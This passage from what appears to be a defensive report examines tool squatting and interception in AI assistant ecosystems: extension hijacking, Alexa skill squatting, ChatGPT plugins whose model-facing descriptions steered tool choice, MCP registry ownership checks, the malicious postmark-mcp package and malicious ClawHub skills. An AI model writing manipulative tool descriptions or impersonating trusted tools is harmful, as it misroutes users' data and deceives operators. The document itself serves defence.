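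Manifest V3, the new format for browser extensions, restricts how extensions change requests much more than how they observe them. An ordinary extension can still observe requests to every site it has permission to access, and it can read the pages. The format therefore did little against extensions that copy data.

### Hijacked searches, imitations and trusted extensions

An extension can request to become the browser's search provider. Chrome then sends every search the user types into the address bar to the site named in the extension's configuration file. This resembles a tool that claims every request, except that the extension needs no persuasive wording.

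Since 2013, Google's store policy has required each extension to have a single, narrow purpose that is easy to understand. An extension that converts PDF files, for example, shouldn't also replace the search engine. Extensions that do replace it must use an official interface for overriding settings, so that Chrome can tell the user what changed and offer to change it back. These rules haven't stopped extensions from hijacking searches. In October 2022, the security company Guardio described 30 that did so while offering to change the colours of web pages. Together they had more than a million installations. The versions in the store contained no malicious code, because the extensions loaded it only after installation.

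Other extensions imitate trusted ones. The security company SquareX demonstrated in early 2025 how an extension could change its appearance after installation:

1. The extension works as an ordinary AI tool, and the user pins its icon to the toolbar.
2. It checks which other extensions the user has and finds a target, such as a password manager.
3. It copies the target's icon and temporarily disables the real extension.
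4. The user clicks the familiar icon, gets a false login form and types in the master password.

Every Chrome extension has its own identifier, which a malicious extension imitating it can't copy, but the toolbar shows only the icon. An AI system's approval prompt has the same weakness if it shows a tool name such as `send_email` without the server's identifier.

In the Cyberhaven case, the attacker compromised a genuine extension instead of imitating one. Cyberhaven sells an extension that helps companies prevent data leaks, which had some 400,000 users. On 24 December 2024, an employee followed a link in an email that appeared to come from the Chrome Web Store and unknowingly gave the attacker permission to publish updates. The attacker released a malicious version early the next morning, and Chrome's automatic updates distributed it for about a day. The malicious version stole login cookies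 and was aimed mainly at Facebook advertising accounts. Investigators soon linked the campaign to dozens of other extensions. Proof of ownership would not have helped, because the name, the identifier and the publisher's account were all genuine.

More recently, researchers have found extensions that collect conversations with AI assistants. In December 2025, the security company Koi reported that Urban VPN Proxy, which had more than six million users on Chrome, had been copying conversations with ChatGPT, Claude, Gemini and other assistants since an update in July. Around the turn of 2026, OX Security described two extensions with about 900,000 users that posed as a legitimate AI sidebar and sent ChatGPT and DeepSeek conversations to their operators. Google had given Urban VPN Proxy and one of the two imitations its "Featured" badge, which is supposed to indicate good practice.

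The AI assistants kept answering normally, so users had no reason to suspect anything. If people open the office assistant in a browser, an extension with permission to read that page can copy invoice 1042 without interacting with the tools. An administrator who restricts MCP servers should therefore restrict extensions too.

### Android's chooser and verified links

An Android app can request an action without naming the app that should perform it. For example, a messaging app may request that Android open a web address. Any installed app can declare in its configuration file that it handles such addresses. When several apps matched, Android traditionally showed a *chooser*, a dialog listing their names and icons, and the user picked one to use just once or every time.

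The chooser prevents a new app from silently taking over, but users have to recognise the right app by its name and icon, both chosen by its developer. The chooser also interrupts users, which makes the option to remember their choice attractive. If they select the wrong app and save that choice, every later request of that kind can go to it.

Google's next solution relied on proof of who owns a domain. With Android App Links, introduced in Android 6 in 2015, the owner of a website publishes a file there that identifies its app and the certificate that signs it. Android fetches the file and compares it with the installed app:

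```
File on bank.example:   app com.bank.app    certificate A1:B2
Installed app 1:        com.bank.app        certificate A1:B2   →  opens the bank's links
Installed app 2:        com.other.app       certificate 9F:04   →  fails the check
```

The second app can claim the bank's address in its configuration file, but it can't change the file on the bank's website. At first, few developers set up this check properly. Liu, Wang and colleagues reported in *Measuring the Insecurity of Mobile Deep Links of Android* (2017) that only 194 of the 8,878 apps that used App Links passed verification. The check achieved little until Android 12, released in 2021, because an app that failed could still appear in the chooser. Since then, web links have opened in the browser unless an app has passed the check or the user has approved it in the settings.

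Android is stricter about background services, where no user is present to answer a dialog. If an app is built for Android 5 or later, Android rejects its request to connect to a service unless the request names the app that provides the service. The office assistant also picks its tools without asking the user to choose, so the same reasoning supports fixed routing for `send_email`.

### Voice assistants and names that sound alike

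Amazon's voice assistant, Alexa, runs add-ons called *skills*. A developer registers an *invocation name* that users say to open the skill, as in "Alexa, open Sleep Sounds". Amazon's computers turn the speech into text, look for a skill with a matching name and pass the user's request to the developer's server. Until April 2017, users had to enable a skill before using it. Alexa can now open skills that users have never enabled, so an attacker may only need to register the right name.

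Kumar, Paccagnella and colleagues (2018), in *Skill Squatting Attacks on Amazon Alexa*, looked for words that Alexa regularly mishears. They played Alexa 11,460 recordings of 188 words, spoken by 60 American speakers, 50 times each. Alexa transcribed 68.9% of them correctly. Most of the errors followed no pattern, but Alexa misheard 24 of the 188 words more than half the time, usually as the same wrong word. It heard "coal" as "call", for example, so an attacker could take users from a skill named Coal by registering one named Call.

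The researchers named this *skill squatting* and tested 27 pairs of names with speakers whose recordings they had not used to find the errors. The false skill opened at least once for 25 of the pairs, which is a lenient measure, but it received more than half the requests for 18 pairs. Its share of requests was 100% for Coal and Call and 0% for Boil and Boyle. The tests all ran in Amazon's developer environment, not in the public store, where thousands of other names might affect the result.

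Some mishearings mainly affected one group of speakers. Alexa opened Pow instead of Pal for 65.9% of requests by speakers from the Midland region of the United States, compared with 37.7% overall. Only ten speakers came from each region, so the exact rates are uncertain, but an attacker could evidently choose a name to target particular victims.

*Dangerous Skills* (Zhang, Mi and colleagues, 2019) described a method that works even when the assistant hears every word correctly. If several skill names match a command, Alexa and Google Assistant prefer the longest. Someone who says "open Sleep Sounds please" may therefore open a skill named Sleep Sounds Please instead of Sleep Sounds. When the researchers asked Amazon Echo owners for examples of their commands, half of them used "please" at least once.

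The researchers chose ten skills on each platform and registered longer versions of their names in test mode. They then counted how many of the false skills opened:

| False name | Alexa | Google Assistant |
|---|---|---|
| Name + "please" | 10 of 10 | 0 of 10 |
| "my" + name | 7 of 10 | 0 of 10 |
| "the" + name | 10 of 10 | 0 of 10 |
| Name + "app" | 10 of 10 | 10 of 10 |
| Name + "plese" | not tested | 10 of 10 |
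| "mai" + name | not tested | 10 of 10 |

Google apparently filtered some suspicious words, but misspellings that sound the same got past the filter every time. Filters for tool descriptions have a similar problem.

### Squatting on the public skill store

Zhang and colleagues also published four skills in Amazon's public store to compete with Sleep and Relaxation Sounds, the skill with the most reviews at the time. Users open it by saying "sleep sounds". One of the four competing skills had exactly the same invocation name, and Amazon approved it. All four were harmless and played sleep sounds. A fifth skill with an unrelated name served as a comparison. These are the results for three weeks:

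| Invocation name | Users | Unrecognised requests per user | Sessions per user that ended before any sound played |
|---|---|---|---|
| sleep sounds please | 325 | 1.11 | 0.73 |
| soothing sleep sounds | 294 | 1.28 | 0.87 |
| the sleep sounds | 144 | 1.11 | 0.45 |
| sleep sounds | 109 | 1.59 | 0.82 |
| incredible fast sleep (comparison) | 200 | 0.56 | 0.11 |

Users of the four competing skills gave up early far more often than users of the comparison skill. More than a fifth of the unrecognised requests were for sounds that only the popular skill offered. Some users had clearly meant to open that skill, but the figures don't show how many. The study's introduction reports 2,699 users in a month, while the four skills in this table had 872 in three weeks, so the total number of users is also uncertain.

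To find out how common confusing names were, the researchers converted every name in the store into *phonemes*, the basic sounds of a language, and calculated how much one sequence had to change to become another. Of 19,670 Alexa skills, 4,718 had a name that sounded the same or nearly the same as another skill's. Excluding identically spelled names, the number was 2,630. One skill was named "me a dog fact", apparently to catch the command "tell me a dog fact".

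Google banned duplicate names for its voice add-ons, and only 4 of the 1,001 had a name that sounded like another's. But its catalogue was about a twentieth the size of Amazon's, so it would have had fewer name clashes even without the ban.

Amazon allowed multiple skills to have the same name, so Alexa had to choose between them. Zhang and colleagues thought the choice might be random. *Are you home alone?* (2020) found a pattern by repeating commands 20 times. If the user had enabled none of the skills with a given name, Alexa opened the most popular one. If the user had enabled one of them, Alexa opened that one. If the user had enabled several with equal ratings, Alexa tended to open the first or last one enabled. Amazon may have changed the method between the two studies. Preferring a skill the user has enabled is sensible, because an attacker can't meet that condition just by registering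 a name.

Kumar and colleagues suggested that Amazon compare the sound of each new skill's name with existing ones before approving the skill. Amazon requires developers to provide documents proving ownership before they use a brand name, according to its *Design the Invocation Name for Your Skill*. Developers can't change an invocation name after publication, according to *Choose the Invocation Name for a Custom Skill*. Certification testers also advise developers on avoiding overlaps, as *Steps to Avoid Overlaps When Choosing an Invocation Name* (2021) explains.

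Later research found gaps in these controls. In *Hey Alexa, is this Skill Safe?*, Lentzsch, Shah and colleagues (2021) analysed 90,194 skills and found that a malicious developer could publish under any company's name. The developer could also change a skill's code after approval, because the code runs on the developer's own server, so freezing the skill's name offers little protection. Amazon confirmed some of the problems and said it was working on countermeasures, according to Ruhr-Universität Bochum, where some of the researchers worked.

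*SkillFence* (2022) reports that a skill named Phitbit, which sounds like the fitness brand Fitbit, passed Amazon's certification. The paper proposes a defence that runs on the user's side, independently of the store. It checks which services the person already uses on the web and on their phone, and allows the matching skills. In tests it covered 90.83% of the skills a user would need, but it also accepted 19.83% of those it should have rejected. For a company that knows which mail and accounts servers it uses, a fixed list would be more accurate than inferring them from usage.

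### ChatGPT's plugin store

OpenAI introduced ChatGPT plugins in March 2023. Each plugin ran on its developer's server and had a configuration file with two descriptions, one for users and one for the model. Once a user enabled a plugin, ChatGPT received the description written for the model and used it to decide when to call the plugin. MCP works nearly the same way, which makes plugins the closest precedent for interception between tools.

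Iqbal, Kohno and Roesner (2023), in *LLM Platform Security*, studied 268 plugins that were in the store on 6 June 2023. They read the plugins' files and tried out suspicious ones in ChatGPT. Twelve plugins appeared able to take requests meant for another plugin or service, and 14 appeared able to take all requests on a topic. Four cases show different ways in which a description could affect ChatGPT:

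| Plugin | Its description | What ChatGPT did |
|---|---|---|
| Expedia | Told ChatGPT, partly in capital letters, to use it for all travel questions | Sent travel questions to Expedia although Trip.com and Klook were also available |
| Lexi Shopper | Mentioned Amazon | Called the plugin although the user had ruled out third-party services |
| Jio | Offered shopping at several stores, including Tira | Called Jio although the user had asked for Tira and enabled Tira's own plugin |
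| AMZPRO | Told ChatGPT to reply in English | Answered an Urdu request in English without using the plugin |

Expedia's plugin is an early example of selection manipulation by an honest business. The AMZPRO case is related to description shadowing, because one plugin's text changed ChatGPT's behaviour in a conversation that didn't use that plugin.

The Jio case is the most worrying for defenders because the user named the service they wanted and its genuine plugin was available, but the request still went to another company. OpenAI restricted each plugin's communication to a known web domain, tirabeauty.com for Tira and jiocommerce.io for Jio, so ChatGPT's software had the information it needed to tell them apart. The model instead chose a plugin by its description. Proof of ownership protects a request only if the client uses it when deciding where to send the call.

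Bad descriptions could also cause misrouting by accident. Tira was described to users as a seller of beauty products, but its description for the model left this out, and ChatGPT sent it requests for groceries. The store also contained two pairs of plugins with identical names and code but different developers. In one pair, both named Upskillr, one copy came from upskillr.ai and the other from an unrelated review site. The review site's server didn't respond, so the researchers couldn't tell whether that copy was malicious.

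The study provides strong evidence that these routes existed but little evidence of how often they worked. Iqbal and colleagues counted plugins capable of attacks rather than actual attacks. They illustrated their cases with individual conversations, and a language model might have chosen differently on another attempt.

OpenAI reviewed plugins before publication, said it would remove any that changed, and prohibited them from including instructions for ChatGPT in their replies. Enforcement was weak. Several plugins included such instructions anyway, and according to Iqbal and colleagues, a single reviewer was responsible for all published plugins. When they reported their findings, OpenAI replied that the issues posed no security risk to the platform. At least one plugin company had also reported a problem that only OpenAI could fix, but OpenAI didn't fix it.

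OpenAI closed the plugin store in the spring of 2024 and replaced plugins with *actions*, which work similarly but belong to a GPT, a customised version of ChatGPT. The person who builds a GPT chooses its actions, so tools from competing publishers are less likely to be available in the same conversation. Whatever OpenAI's reasons were, this change probably did more to prevent interception than the store's rules had. Current MCP clients load servers from several publishers at once, so their tools compete within a conversation again.

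Iqbal and colleagues recommended that platforms host the plugins' code themselves so that they could review each update. They also recommended permissions like those on phones and a separate compartment for each plugin. The three researchers later helped develop IsolateGPT, which implements such compartments.

### What carries over to AI tools

A fixed order of precedence among tools is useful if attackers can't influence it. An operator can rank the mail server above the notes server for email and keep that ranking when either one updates. Chrome's rule shows why installation time is a poor basis for the ranking.

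Verifying ownership is also useful for AI tools. Android's check is a good model because a rival app's developer can't pass it by copying a name or description. For MCP servers, the proof of ownership would come from a registry or a company's own records, and the client would have to check it on each call. A tool with a verified owner can still behave badly, as the Cyberhaven case showed.

The single-purpose rule gives reviewers something definite to check. If the office has approved the notes server for meeting notes, `find_records` breaks the rule if its description mentions invoices, even if the description contains no commands. Whoever approves the server has to write down its purpose, since a dishonest publisher will otherwise describe it as broadly as possible. Reviewers can't use the rule to detect a notes tool that does its stated job and also copies the notes elsewhere.

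A further restriction could follow the example of Manifest V3, under which extensions now give the browser rules to carry out. A publisher could likewise supply a template instead of a tool such as `format_invoice`. The client would fill in the template itself, so the notes server would never receive the invoice. This works only for simple, predictable jobs, and a reviewer would still have to check the template for a false bank account number.

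The main difference is how a platform matches a request to an add-on. Firefox has a function that lets extension developers check in advance whether a rule matches a given request, and the result doesn't depend on how appealing the rule sounds. Matching speech is less exact, and Alexa sometimes transcribed the same recording differently. Even so, researchers could calculate the distance between two names and list risky pairs before anyone attacked them.

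No comparable distance reliably separates an honest tool description from a manipulative one. Dai and colleagues found that a false description can be close in meaning to the genuine one and still attract most requests. An honest competing tool may have a similar description too. The model's choice also depends on the user's wording and the other tools in its context, so adding one server or rephrasing a request can change the result.

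## Registries and proof of who owns a name

In *tool squatting*, an attacker registers a name that resembles or anticipates a trusted one. If an employee installs an imitation of the company's mail server, the client will send it every email. *Securing GenAI Multi-Agent Systems Against Tool Squatting* (Narajala, Huang and Habler, 2025) uses the term more broadly to include tampering with a genuine tool's description. The narrower meaning is more useful here because proof of ownership can help against false names but not false descriptions.

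### Lessons from package registries

Programmers build much of their software from *packages*, ready-made pieces of code that they download from public registries such as npm for JavaScript and PyPI for Python. Many MCP servers are packages in the same registries, so the old attacks on packages work on them too.

In *typosquatting*, an attacker registers a likely misspelling of a popular name. In 2017, for example, someone published a package called `crossenv` on npm to catch people looking for `cross-env`. The package copied settings that often include passwords. npm accepted the name because nobody else was using it.

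*Dependency confusion* doesn't need a typing mistake. In 2021, the security researcher Alex Birsan found the names of companies' internal packages in public code and registered the same names in public registries. Some installation programs searched both the company's registry and the public one, then took the higher version number:

```
Company's registry:   acme-billing   version 1.4.0
Public registry:      acme-billing   version 99.0.0   →  installed
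```

Birsan's test code ran inside more than 35 organisations, including Apple and Microsoft. A company with its own list of MCP servers could make the same mistake, using a public entry in place of its own, if its client also searches a public registry. The client should take the company's mail server, for example, only from the company's list, even if a public entry has a higher version number.

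Registries also offer names that include their owner. On npm, only the owner of the `@acme` account can publish `@acme/billing`. This helps people who use the full name, but anyone can still register a similar name without the prefix. In June 2026, someone published `mcp-server-postgres`, which imitated an official MCP server whose name included its owner. According to *MAL-2026-5481* (2026), an entry in OSV, a public database of software vulnerabilities and malicious packages, the package sent each computer's name and current folder to an outside address during installation. The publisher described the package as research into this kind of confusion.

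Names for MCP servers are especially easy to confuse because developers add "mcp" and "server" in no fixed order. *A First Look at the Security Issues in the Model Context Protocol* (Li and Gao, 2025) found 408 groups of npm packages whose names differed only in these additions, such as `package-mcp` and `package-mcp-server`. In about 80% of the groups, the packages had different maintainers. Most of these packages may be honest projects for the same product, but a user can't tell from the name which one the product's owner wrote.

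### How the official MCP Registry verifies a name

The MCP project launched its own registry in September 2025 (Model Context Protocol, 2025). At the end of November 2026 it was still in preview, with a warning that its data might be reset. The registry stores information about servers, such as their names, descriptions and locations, while the code stays on npm, PyPI or another host.

Every name in the registry begins with a namespace, and a publisher has to prove control of that namespace before using it. Model Context Protocol's authentication guide gives three ways to do this:

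| Proof | What the publisher does | Resulting name |
|---|---|---|
| GitHub login | Logs in to a GitHub account | `io.github.<account>/<server>` |
| DNS record | Adds a public key to the domain's DNS records, the directory entries that tell computers where to find it | `<reversed domain>/<server>` |
| Hosted file | Puts a public key in a file at a fixed address on the domain's website | `<reversed domain>/<server>` |

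Suppose the notes developer owns the domain notes.example and has published the server's code on npm as `notes-mcp`. Listing it in the registry takes five steps:

1. The developer creates a pair of cryptographic keys, keeps the private key and puts the public one in the domain's DNS records.
2. The registry's publishing program signs a login request with the private key.
3. The registry fetches the public key from notes.example and checks the signature. The developer may now publish names that begin with `example.notes/`.
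4. The developer submits a file called `server.json`, which gives the server's name and the location of its package.
5. The registry opens the package on npm and checks that it contains the same server name.

The last step requires the two entries to match:

```
server.json, in the registry:      name     example.notes/notes-server
                                   package  npm, notes-mcp
package.json, in the npm package:  mcpName  example.notes/notes-server
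```

Without this match, the developer could list somebody else's popular package under their own namespace. Only a person who can edit the package can add the matching name.

The check depends on the type of package, according to Model Context Protocol's guide to package types. PyPI, NuGet and Cargo packages need the name in their public description, and container images need it in a label. For MCPB, a format for ready-to-run bundles, the registry instead requires the entry to include a hash of the file, but doesn't check that the hash is correct. Clients check it before installation, which shows that the file matches the entry but not that the entry's publisher made the file.

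The registry now lets only the owners of a GitHub organisation publish servers in its name. Previously, any member could have published or overwritten one.

### What a verified name proves

A verified name shows that the publisher controlled a certain account or domain when they published the entry. The following names could all pass, if the company's real mail provider owned mail.example:

| Name in the registry | What the publisher had to control | Is it the mail provider? |
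|---|---|---|
| `example.mail/mail-server` | The domain mail.example | Yes |
| `example.mai1/mail-server` | The domain mai1.example, with a digit 1 in place of the letter l | No |
| `io.github.mail-example/mail-server` | A GitHub account named mail-example | Not necessarily, since anyone could have opened the account |
| `example.notes/notes-server` | The domain notes.example | No, but it can still offer a tool called `send_email` |

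The registry can't reserve the tool name `send_email` for the mail provider because it doesn't store tool names. For *Same Name, Different Server*, Kraishan (2026) downloaded the whole registry in August 2026 and found no tool definitions in its 72,606 version records, because the format has no place for them. Clients therefore have to handle duplicate tool names themselves. For the same reason, the registry can't compare a tool's description with what the tool does.

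An account name can also pass to a new owner. GitHub releases the name of a deleted account after 90 days, according to Li and Gao. In mid-2025, they studied four registries that link to code on GitHub and found 212 entries that linked to account names anyone could register. Another 304 entries still used the old names of renamed accounts. GitHub redirects visitors from an old name to the new one, but the redirect ends if someone registers the old name and recreates the project there.

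Li and Gao collected their data before the official registry opened. The registry's authentication guide describes no check for a change of owner, so someone who takes over an abandoned account or an expired domain could presumably publish under the previous owner's namespace.

An attacker can also misuse an account that its owner still holds. On MCP.so, a large open registry, Li and Gao found nine GitHub access tokens that developers had pasted into public examples, and five still worked. A working token could let an attacker put malicious tool descriptions into a genuine server under its existing name.

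### What the registry removes

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) Registry has a permissive moderation policy. Its maintainers remove illegal content, malware, spam and servers that don't work, but they leave up servers that have security vulnerabilities or do the same job as others. The May 2026 version of the policy advises users to assume "minimal-to-no moderation".

It is unclear whether the rules prohibit impersonation. The launch announcement listed it as a violation people could report, but the May 2026 policy doesn't mention it. An imitation that contains malware clearly breaks the rules, but one that starts out harmless and turns malicious only after gaining users might not.

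The spam rules cover one form of selection manipulation. Maintainers may remove a server whose registry description is full of marketing copy unrelated to what the server does. This provision does not apply to the server's tool descriptions.

When the maintainers remove a server, they mark it as "deleted" but usually leave its details available to other programs. A marketplace that copies the registry without checking for this mark will keep offering the server.

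The registry also leaves security scanning to the package registries and to the marketplaces that copy its data. Model Context Protocol's overview describes those marketplaces, rather than AI applications, as the registry's intended users. This division is reasonable as long as the marketplaces do the scanning. A listing in the official registry doesn't mean anyone has examined the code, so administrators should ask a marketplace what it checks.

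### Two flaws in the ownership checks

In May 2026, OSV published reports of two flaws in the registry's software that affected proof of ownership. It rated both low severity, and the maintainers have fixed them.

OSV's *CVE-2026-45781* (2026) describes a flaw in how the registry checked container images, which bundle a program with everything it needs to run. The registry normally checked an image's label for the matching server name. If the image's host refused the request because it had received too many requests, the registry skipped the check and accepted the entry. A publisher could then list an image they didn't control under their own namespace. Other package types were unaffected because the registry rejected their entries if it couldn't reach the package. Version 1.7.9 fixed the flaw.

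An attacker could use this flaw to make their own entry look more credible by attaching the mail provider's genuine image to it, but could not publish under the provider's namespace. A company that writes its own ownership check should treat an unfinished check as a failed one.

OSV's *CVE-2026-44428* (2026) describes a flaw that could have let an attacker publish under someone else's name. When developers publish automatically from GitHub, GitHub issues a token that identifies them. Before version 1.7.6, the token was valid for every registry that ran the same software, instead of just the one the developer had chosen. An attack would have had three steps:

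1. The mail provider publishes its server to a registry that the attacker runs or has broken into.
2. The attacker copies the token that the provider's publishing program sends.
3. The attacker presents the token to the official registry and receives permission to publish under the provider's `io.github` namespace.

The rating is probably low because the attack needs a victim who publishes to a hostile registry. That could become more likely as more companies and marketplaces run their own registries. GitLab's *Advisories for Golang/Github.com/Modelcontextprotocol/Registry package* lists two further flaws from 2026. One let a publisher put malicious code into the registry's public web page, and the other concerned the protection that stops the domain check from connecting to private networks.

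### The postmark-mcp package

The clearest known case of tool squatting involved Postmark, a company that sends email for other businesses. Postmark had published the code of its MCP server on GitHub but not on npm. A developer copied the code and published it on npm as `postmark-mcp`, the name Postmark used on GitHub. The first 15 versions worked normally. Version 1.0.16, released on 17 September 2025 according to The Hacker News (2025), added one line that sent a blind copy of every email to an address the developer controlled.

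The security company Koi discovered the change and called it the first malicious MCP server found in real use. Koi sells protection against such packages, but other sources support its account. Postmark confirmed it had nothing to do with the package, and OSV's *MAL-2025-47604* (2025), an entry credited to Google's open-source security team, lists the same version as malicious.

Koi's estimate of the damage is much less certain. Koi counted 1,500 downloads a week, guessed that 20% were in active use, and estimated that the package affected about 300 organisations and stole 3,000 to 15,000 emails a day. Paubox, an email company, reports only 1,643 downloads over the package's lifetime. Downloads also include automated systems and repeated installations, so the number of victims could be far smaller than 300.

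The model called `send_email` with the right recipient, and the server's code added the extra copy, so a gateway that checks arguments would have approved the call. Someone reading the mail service's logs could have found the unfamiliar address.

The official registry's checks would not have stopped this package either. The developer controlled both a GitHub account and the npm package, so they could have obtained a verified name beginning with `io.github` and their own account name. A careful user would have seen from that name that the package didn't come from Postmark. Postmark now advises people to use only packages listed in its official documentation. Following that advice would have prevented the installation.

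The developer deleted the package from npm after Koi asked for an explanation. As Koi points out, deletion doesn't affect copies that people have already installed.

### Malicious skills on ClawHub

OpenClaw is an AI assistant that people run on their own computers, and ClawHub is its marketplace for *skills*. A skill is a folder of written instructions for the assistant, sometimes with programs to run. The assistant picks skills by their descriptions, as it does tools, but a skill's instructions can direct everything the assistant does next.

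Attackers targeted ClawHub almost immediately. Koi found 341 malicious skills among 2,857, or 12% (The Hacker News, February 2026). Nearly all of them told users to install a supposed requirement that was actually a program for stealing passwords and other data from Apple computers. *Towards Secure Agent Skills* (Li, Wu and colleagues, 2026) puts the campaign's total at 1,184 or more malicious skills.

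*From Instructions to Exploits* (2026), a later academic study, found a much lower proportion. It examined 66,157 skills on ClawHub as of 20 April 2026 and confirmed 627 as malicious, just under 1%. By then the marketplace was far larger and had begun scanning for malware, so the two figures aren't directly comparable. Only 23 of the 627 were still identifiable in July, and all 23 carried a warning label.

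Scanning has helped, but not reliably. ClawHub uses three scanners, and *After the Party* (2026) found that they disagreed on 38% of the skills that all three had examined (23,702 of 61,990). Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, found five harmful skills that remained available between February and May 2026. One hid its malicious instructions in a file padded to 22 megabytes, which is larger than many scanners will read. Two others used the name of TradingView, a popular service for traders, and one of them had passed the automatic audit. Palo Alto Networks sells Koi's product, so the two companies are not independent sources.

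### Lookalike servers

UpGuard (2026), another security vendor, took 43 brand names from verified MCP servers and searched for them among unverified ones. For every official server, it found between 3 and 15 unverified servers with the same brand in their names. One search for HubSpot, a sales and marketing service, returned nine servers in active use, only one of which came from HubSpot.

These are only matches between names and may be harmless. For example, a programmer who writes a useful HubSpot server and names it honestly counts as a lookalike. Still, the figures show that users can infer little from a brand name about who wrote a server. In the Smithery registry, the most used server for GitHub ran code from an individual's account, although GitHub's own server was also listed.

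UpGuard also examined 18,000 public Claude Code settings files and found misspelled server names in some of them. Most differed from the correct name only in capitalization. The misspellings show that people make the mistakes typosquatters depend on, but UpGuard doesn't report that any of them led to a malicious server.

### Has anyone intercepted calls between tools outside research?

The postmark-mcp case is interception at installation, because users who wanted Postmark's server got someone else's. Neither this case nor any of the ClawHub incidents described above involved two tools competing inside one assistant. *MalSkillBench* (2026) classified 703 malicious skills found on ClawHub and concluded that most were ordinary software attacks in a new form and came from a few large campaigns.

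The closest case is `money-radar`, a financial advice skill that Unit 42 found. It made the assistant fetch a list of about 60 products from the publisher's website and always recommend them through links that earned the publisher a commission. The publisher could change the list at any time. The skill deliberately steered users toward products for money, but it did not redirect calls meant for another tool.

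Two large surveys looked for hostile tool descriptions and found few. Li and Gao found 18 servers with suspicious descriptions across four registries, most of them demonstrations for teaching or research. Five had descriptions with instructions to call another tool by name, apparently without harmful intent. In one email server, for example, the description of the tool that lists messages included an instruction to use `mark_email_as_handled` afterwards. If another server offered a tool with that name, the model could call that tool instead.

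Kraishan searched for hidden commands in the tool descriptions of 14,353 servers and found none, which would put the true rate below 0.03%. That limit is too low, because the program extracted tool definitions from only 4,238 of the 13,051 code collections it searched. The same calculation for those 4,238 gives a limit of about 0.09%. Both surveys also looked for suspicious words and patterns, so they would have missed a description that only praises its own tool.

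These sources contain no confirmed case of a malicious tool taking or altering another tool's calls in ordinary use. That is only weak evidence that it doesn't happen, because a company whose assistant chose the wrong invoice tool might never find out, or might treat it as a model error. Defenders should give priority to impostor packages, which attackers have already used, but should not ignore the attacks that have worked in every kind of laboratory test.

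### Open, curated and company-run registries

Registries differ mainly in who decides what goes in:

| Type | Who can add a server | What it prevents | Main drawback |
|---|---|---|---|
| Open, such as MCP.so | Anyone | Very little | Users must check everything |
| Open with verified names, such as the official registry | Anyone with a GitHub account or domain | Publishing under someone else's namespace | Lookalike names still pass |
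| Curated, such as GitHub's registry | Publishers that the registry's operator selects | Most imitations | Small selection |
| Company-run | The company's administrators | Installation of unapproved servers, if clients enforce the list | Work for the administrators |

UpGuard counted 57 servers in GitHub's registry, about 3,500 in Smithery and more than 17,000 in MCP.so. Only 8% of a sample of Smithery's servers had a badge for official vendors. UpGuard put the official registry at about 1,000 servers in April 2026, but Kraishan counted 21,643 four months later. Either the registry grew twentyfold or UpGuard's count was incomplete, so UpGuard's finding that the official registry had the fewest lookalikes may be out of date.

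Popularity can't replace curation. Kraishan found almost no correlation between a server's number of GitHub stars and the number of security weaknesses in its code. Among the most popular tenth of servers, 7.5% had serious warnings, compared with 11.1% overall. These warnings indicate weaknesses rather than malice. An attacker can also buy stars or wait for them, as the developer of `postmark-mcp` waited for users.

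A company can run its own registry using the official one's published interface, so that existing applications can read it. Some clients, such as GitHub Copilot, can limit developers to servers in a registry that their organisation chooses, according to *Model Context Protocol Registry*, a set of personal notes. A company that uses a vendor's registry service should keep its own copy of its approved list in case the vendor ends the service. Google Cloud's *Cloud API Registry release notes* show that Google ended Cloud API Registry's support for MCP servers in July 2026, less than eight months after the preview began.

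Narajala and colleagues propose a stricter design, in which administrators register both the tools and the AI agents that may use them. An agent sees only the tools that its rules allow. Before each use, it requests access, and the system issues a short-lived credential for that tool alone. In the office, the notes developer couldn't add a server, and an agent for meeting notes couldn't find `send_email`.

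The design also gives each tool a trust score, for example from 0 to 100. The score depends on whether the tool is up to date, whether its components have known vulnerabilities and how quickly its vendor fixes them. An administrator can set a minimum score for each task.

Such a score measures how well software is maintained, not whether its publisher is honest. The malicious version 1.0.16 of `postmark-mcp` differed from the harmless version 1.0.15 by a single line, and could have scored higher because it was the newest release. The score can help an administrator find neglected software, but it should never outweigh doubts about who the publisher is.

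Narajala and colleagues outline how to build the design but did not test it, and they leave the formula for the score and simulated attacks to future work. The basic principle doesn't need much testing, since a server that nobody can install can't intercept calls. But it remains unknown how well administrators recognise a bad server and whether employees would bypass a slow approval process. The design also assumes a trustworthy administrator, although one of the paper's examples involves a dishonest one. Requiring two people to approve each server, which the paper mentions as an option, would reduce that risk.

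### How to admit a server

An office can apply the following procedure to the notes server before anyone connects it:

1. **Write down the purpose.** The office needs to search and write meeting notes. If an approved server already does this, the request ends here.
2. **Start from the publisher's own website.** The administrator goes to notes.example and follows its link to the package, instead of searching a registry for "notes". If the website doesn't mention an MCP server, the administrator asks the publisher.
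3. **Compare the full name.** The registry entry should begin with `example.notes/`, character for character, and should not be marked as deleted. The administrator copies the name into the configuration instead of retyping it.
4. **Check the package and its owner.** The name inside the package should match the entry. The link to the code should work without redirecting to a different account. For a server that runs on the publisher's computers, its address should belong to notes.example or to a host that the publisher confirms.
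5. **Compare the tools with the purpose.** The administrator lists the tools in an isolated test client with no access to mail or accounts. The server offers `search_notes`, `create_note`, `find_records` and `send_email`. The last two have nothing to do with meeting notes, and `send_email` duplicates a sensitive tool.
6. **Review the definitions and the code.** Somebody reads every description and parameter of the tools that remain, and records the exact version they reviewed.
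7. **Limit and record the approval.** Two people approve the server for certain tools and sessions, with a date for the next review.

The resulting record might look like this:

```
server           example.notes/notes-server
package          npm, notes-mcp, version 2.3.1, hash recorded
purpose          search and write meeting notes
allowed tools    search_notes, create_note
blocked tools    find_records, send_email
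sessions         notes only, never with mail or accounts
approved by      two named administrators
next review      in six months, or at any change
```

The notes developer passes steps 2 to 4 because they own notes.example. Step 5 raises a warning because two of the four tools don't fit the stated purpose. The administrator could reasonably reject the whole server, especially if the publisher has no good explanation for `send_email`.

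The procedure takes time, and a small office may not be able to review code. Such an office can shorten it by choosing servers from a curated registry and following only steps 1, 2, 5 and 7. A full review is worth the delay for a server that can send messages, make payments or read confidential files.

Finally, the administrator has to make the clients enforce the list, or employees can still install servers on their own. Someone should also compare the installed servers with new malware reports and registry deletions. If the notes server appears in either, the office has to uninstall it from every computer and replace any passwords or tokens it could have read.

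## Reviewing tool definitions and catching later changes

When the office approves the notes server, it approves the tool definitions the server supplied that day, but the developer can replace them the next morning. A review therefore protects the office only if reviewers check the definitions for interception and somebody notices later changes.

Many people leave the review to OpenAI or Anthropic, which both run directories of outside tools for their assistants. OpenAI calls the entries *plugins*, a name it also used in its first store, and Anthropic calls the MCP servers in its directory *connectors*.

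### What the directories forbid

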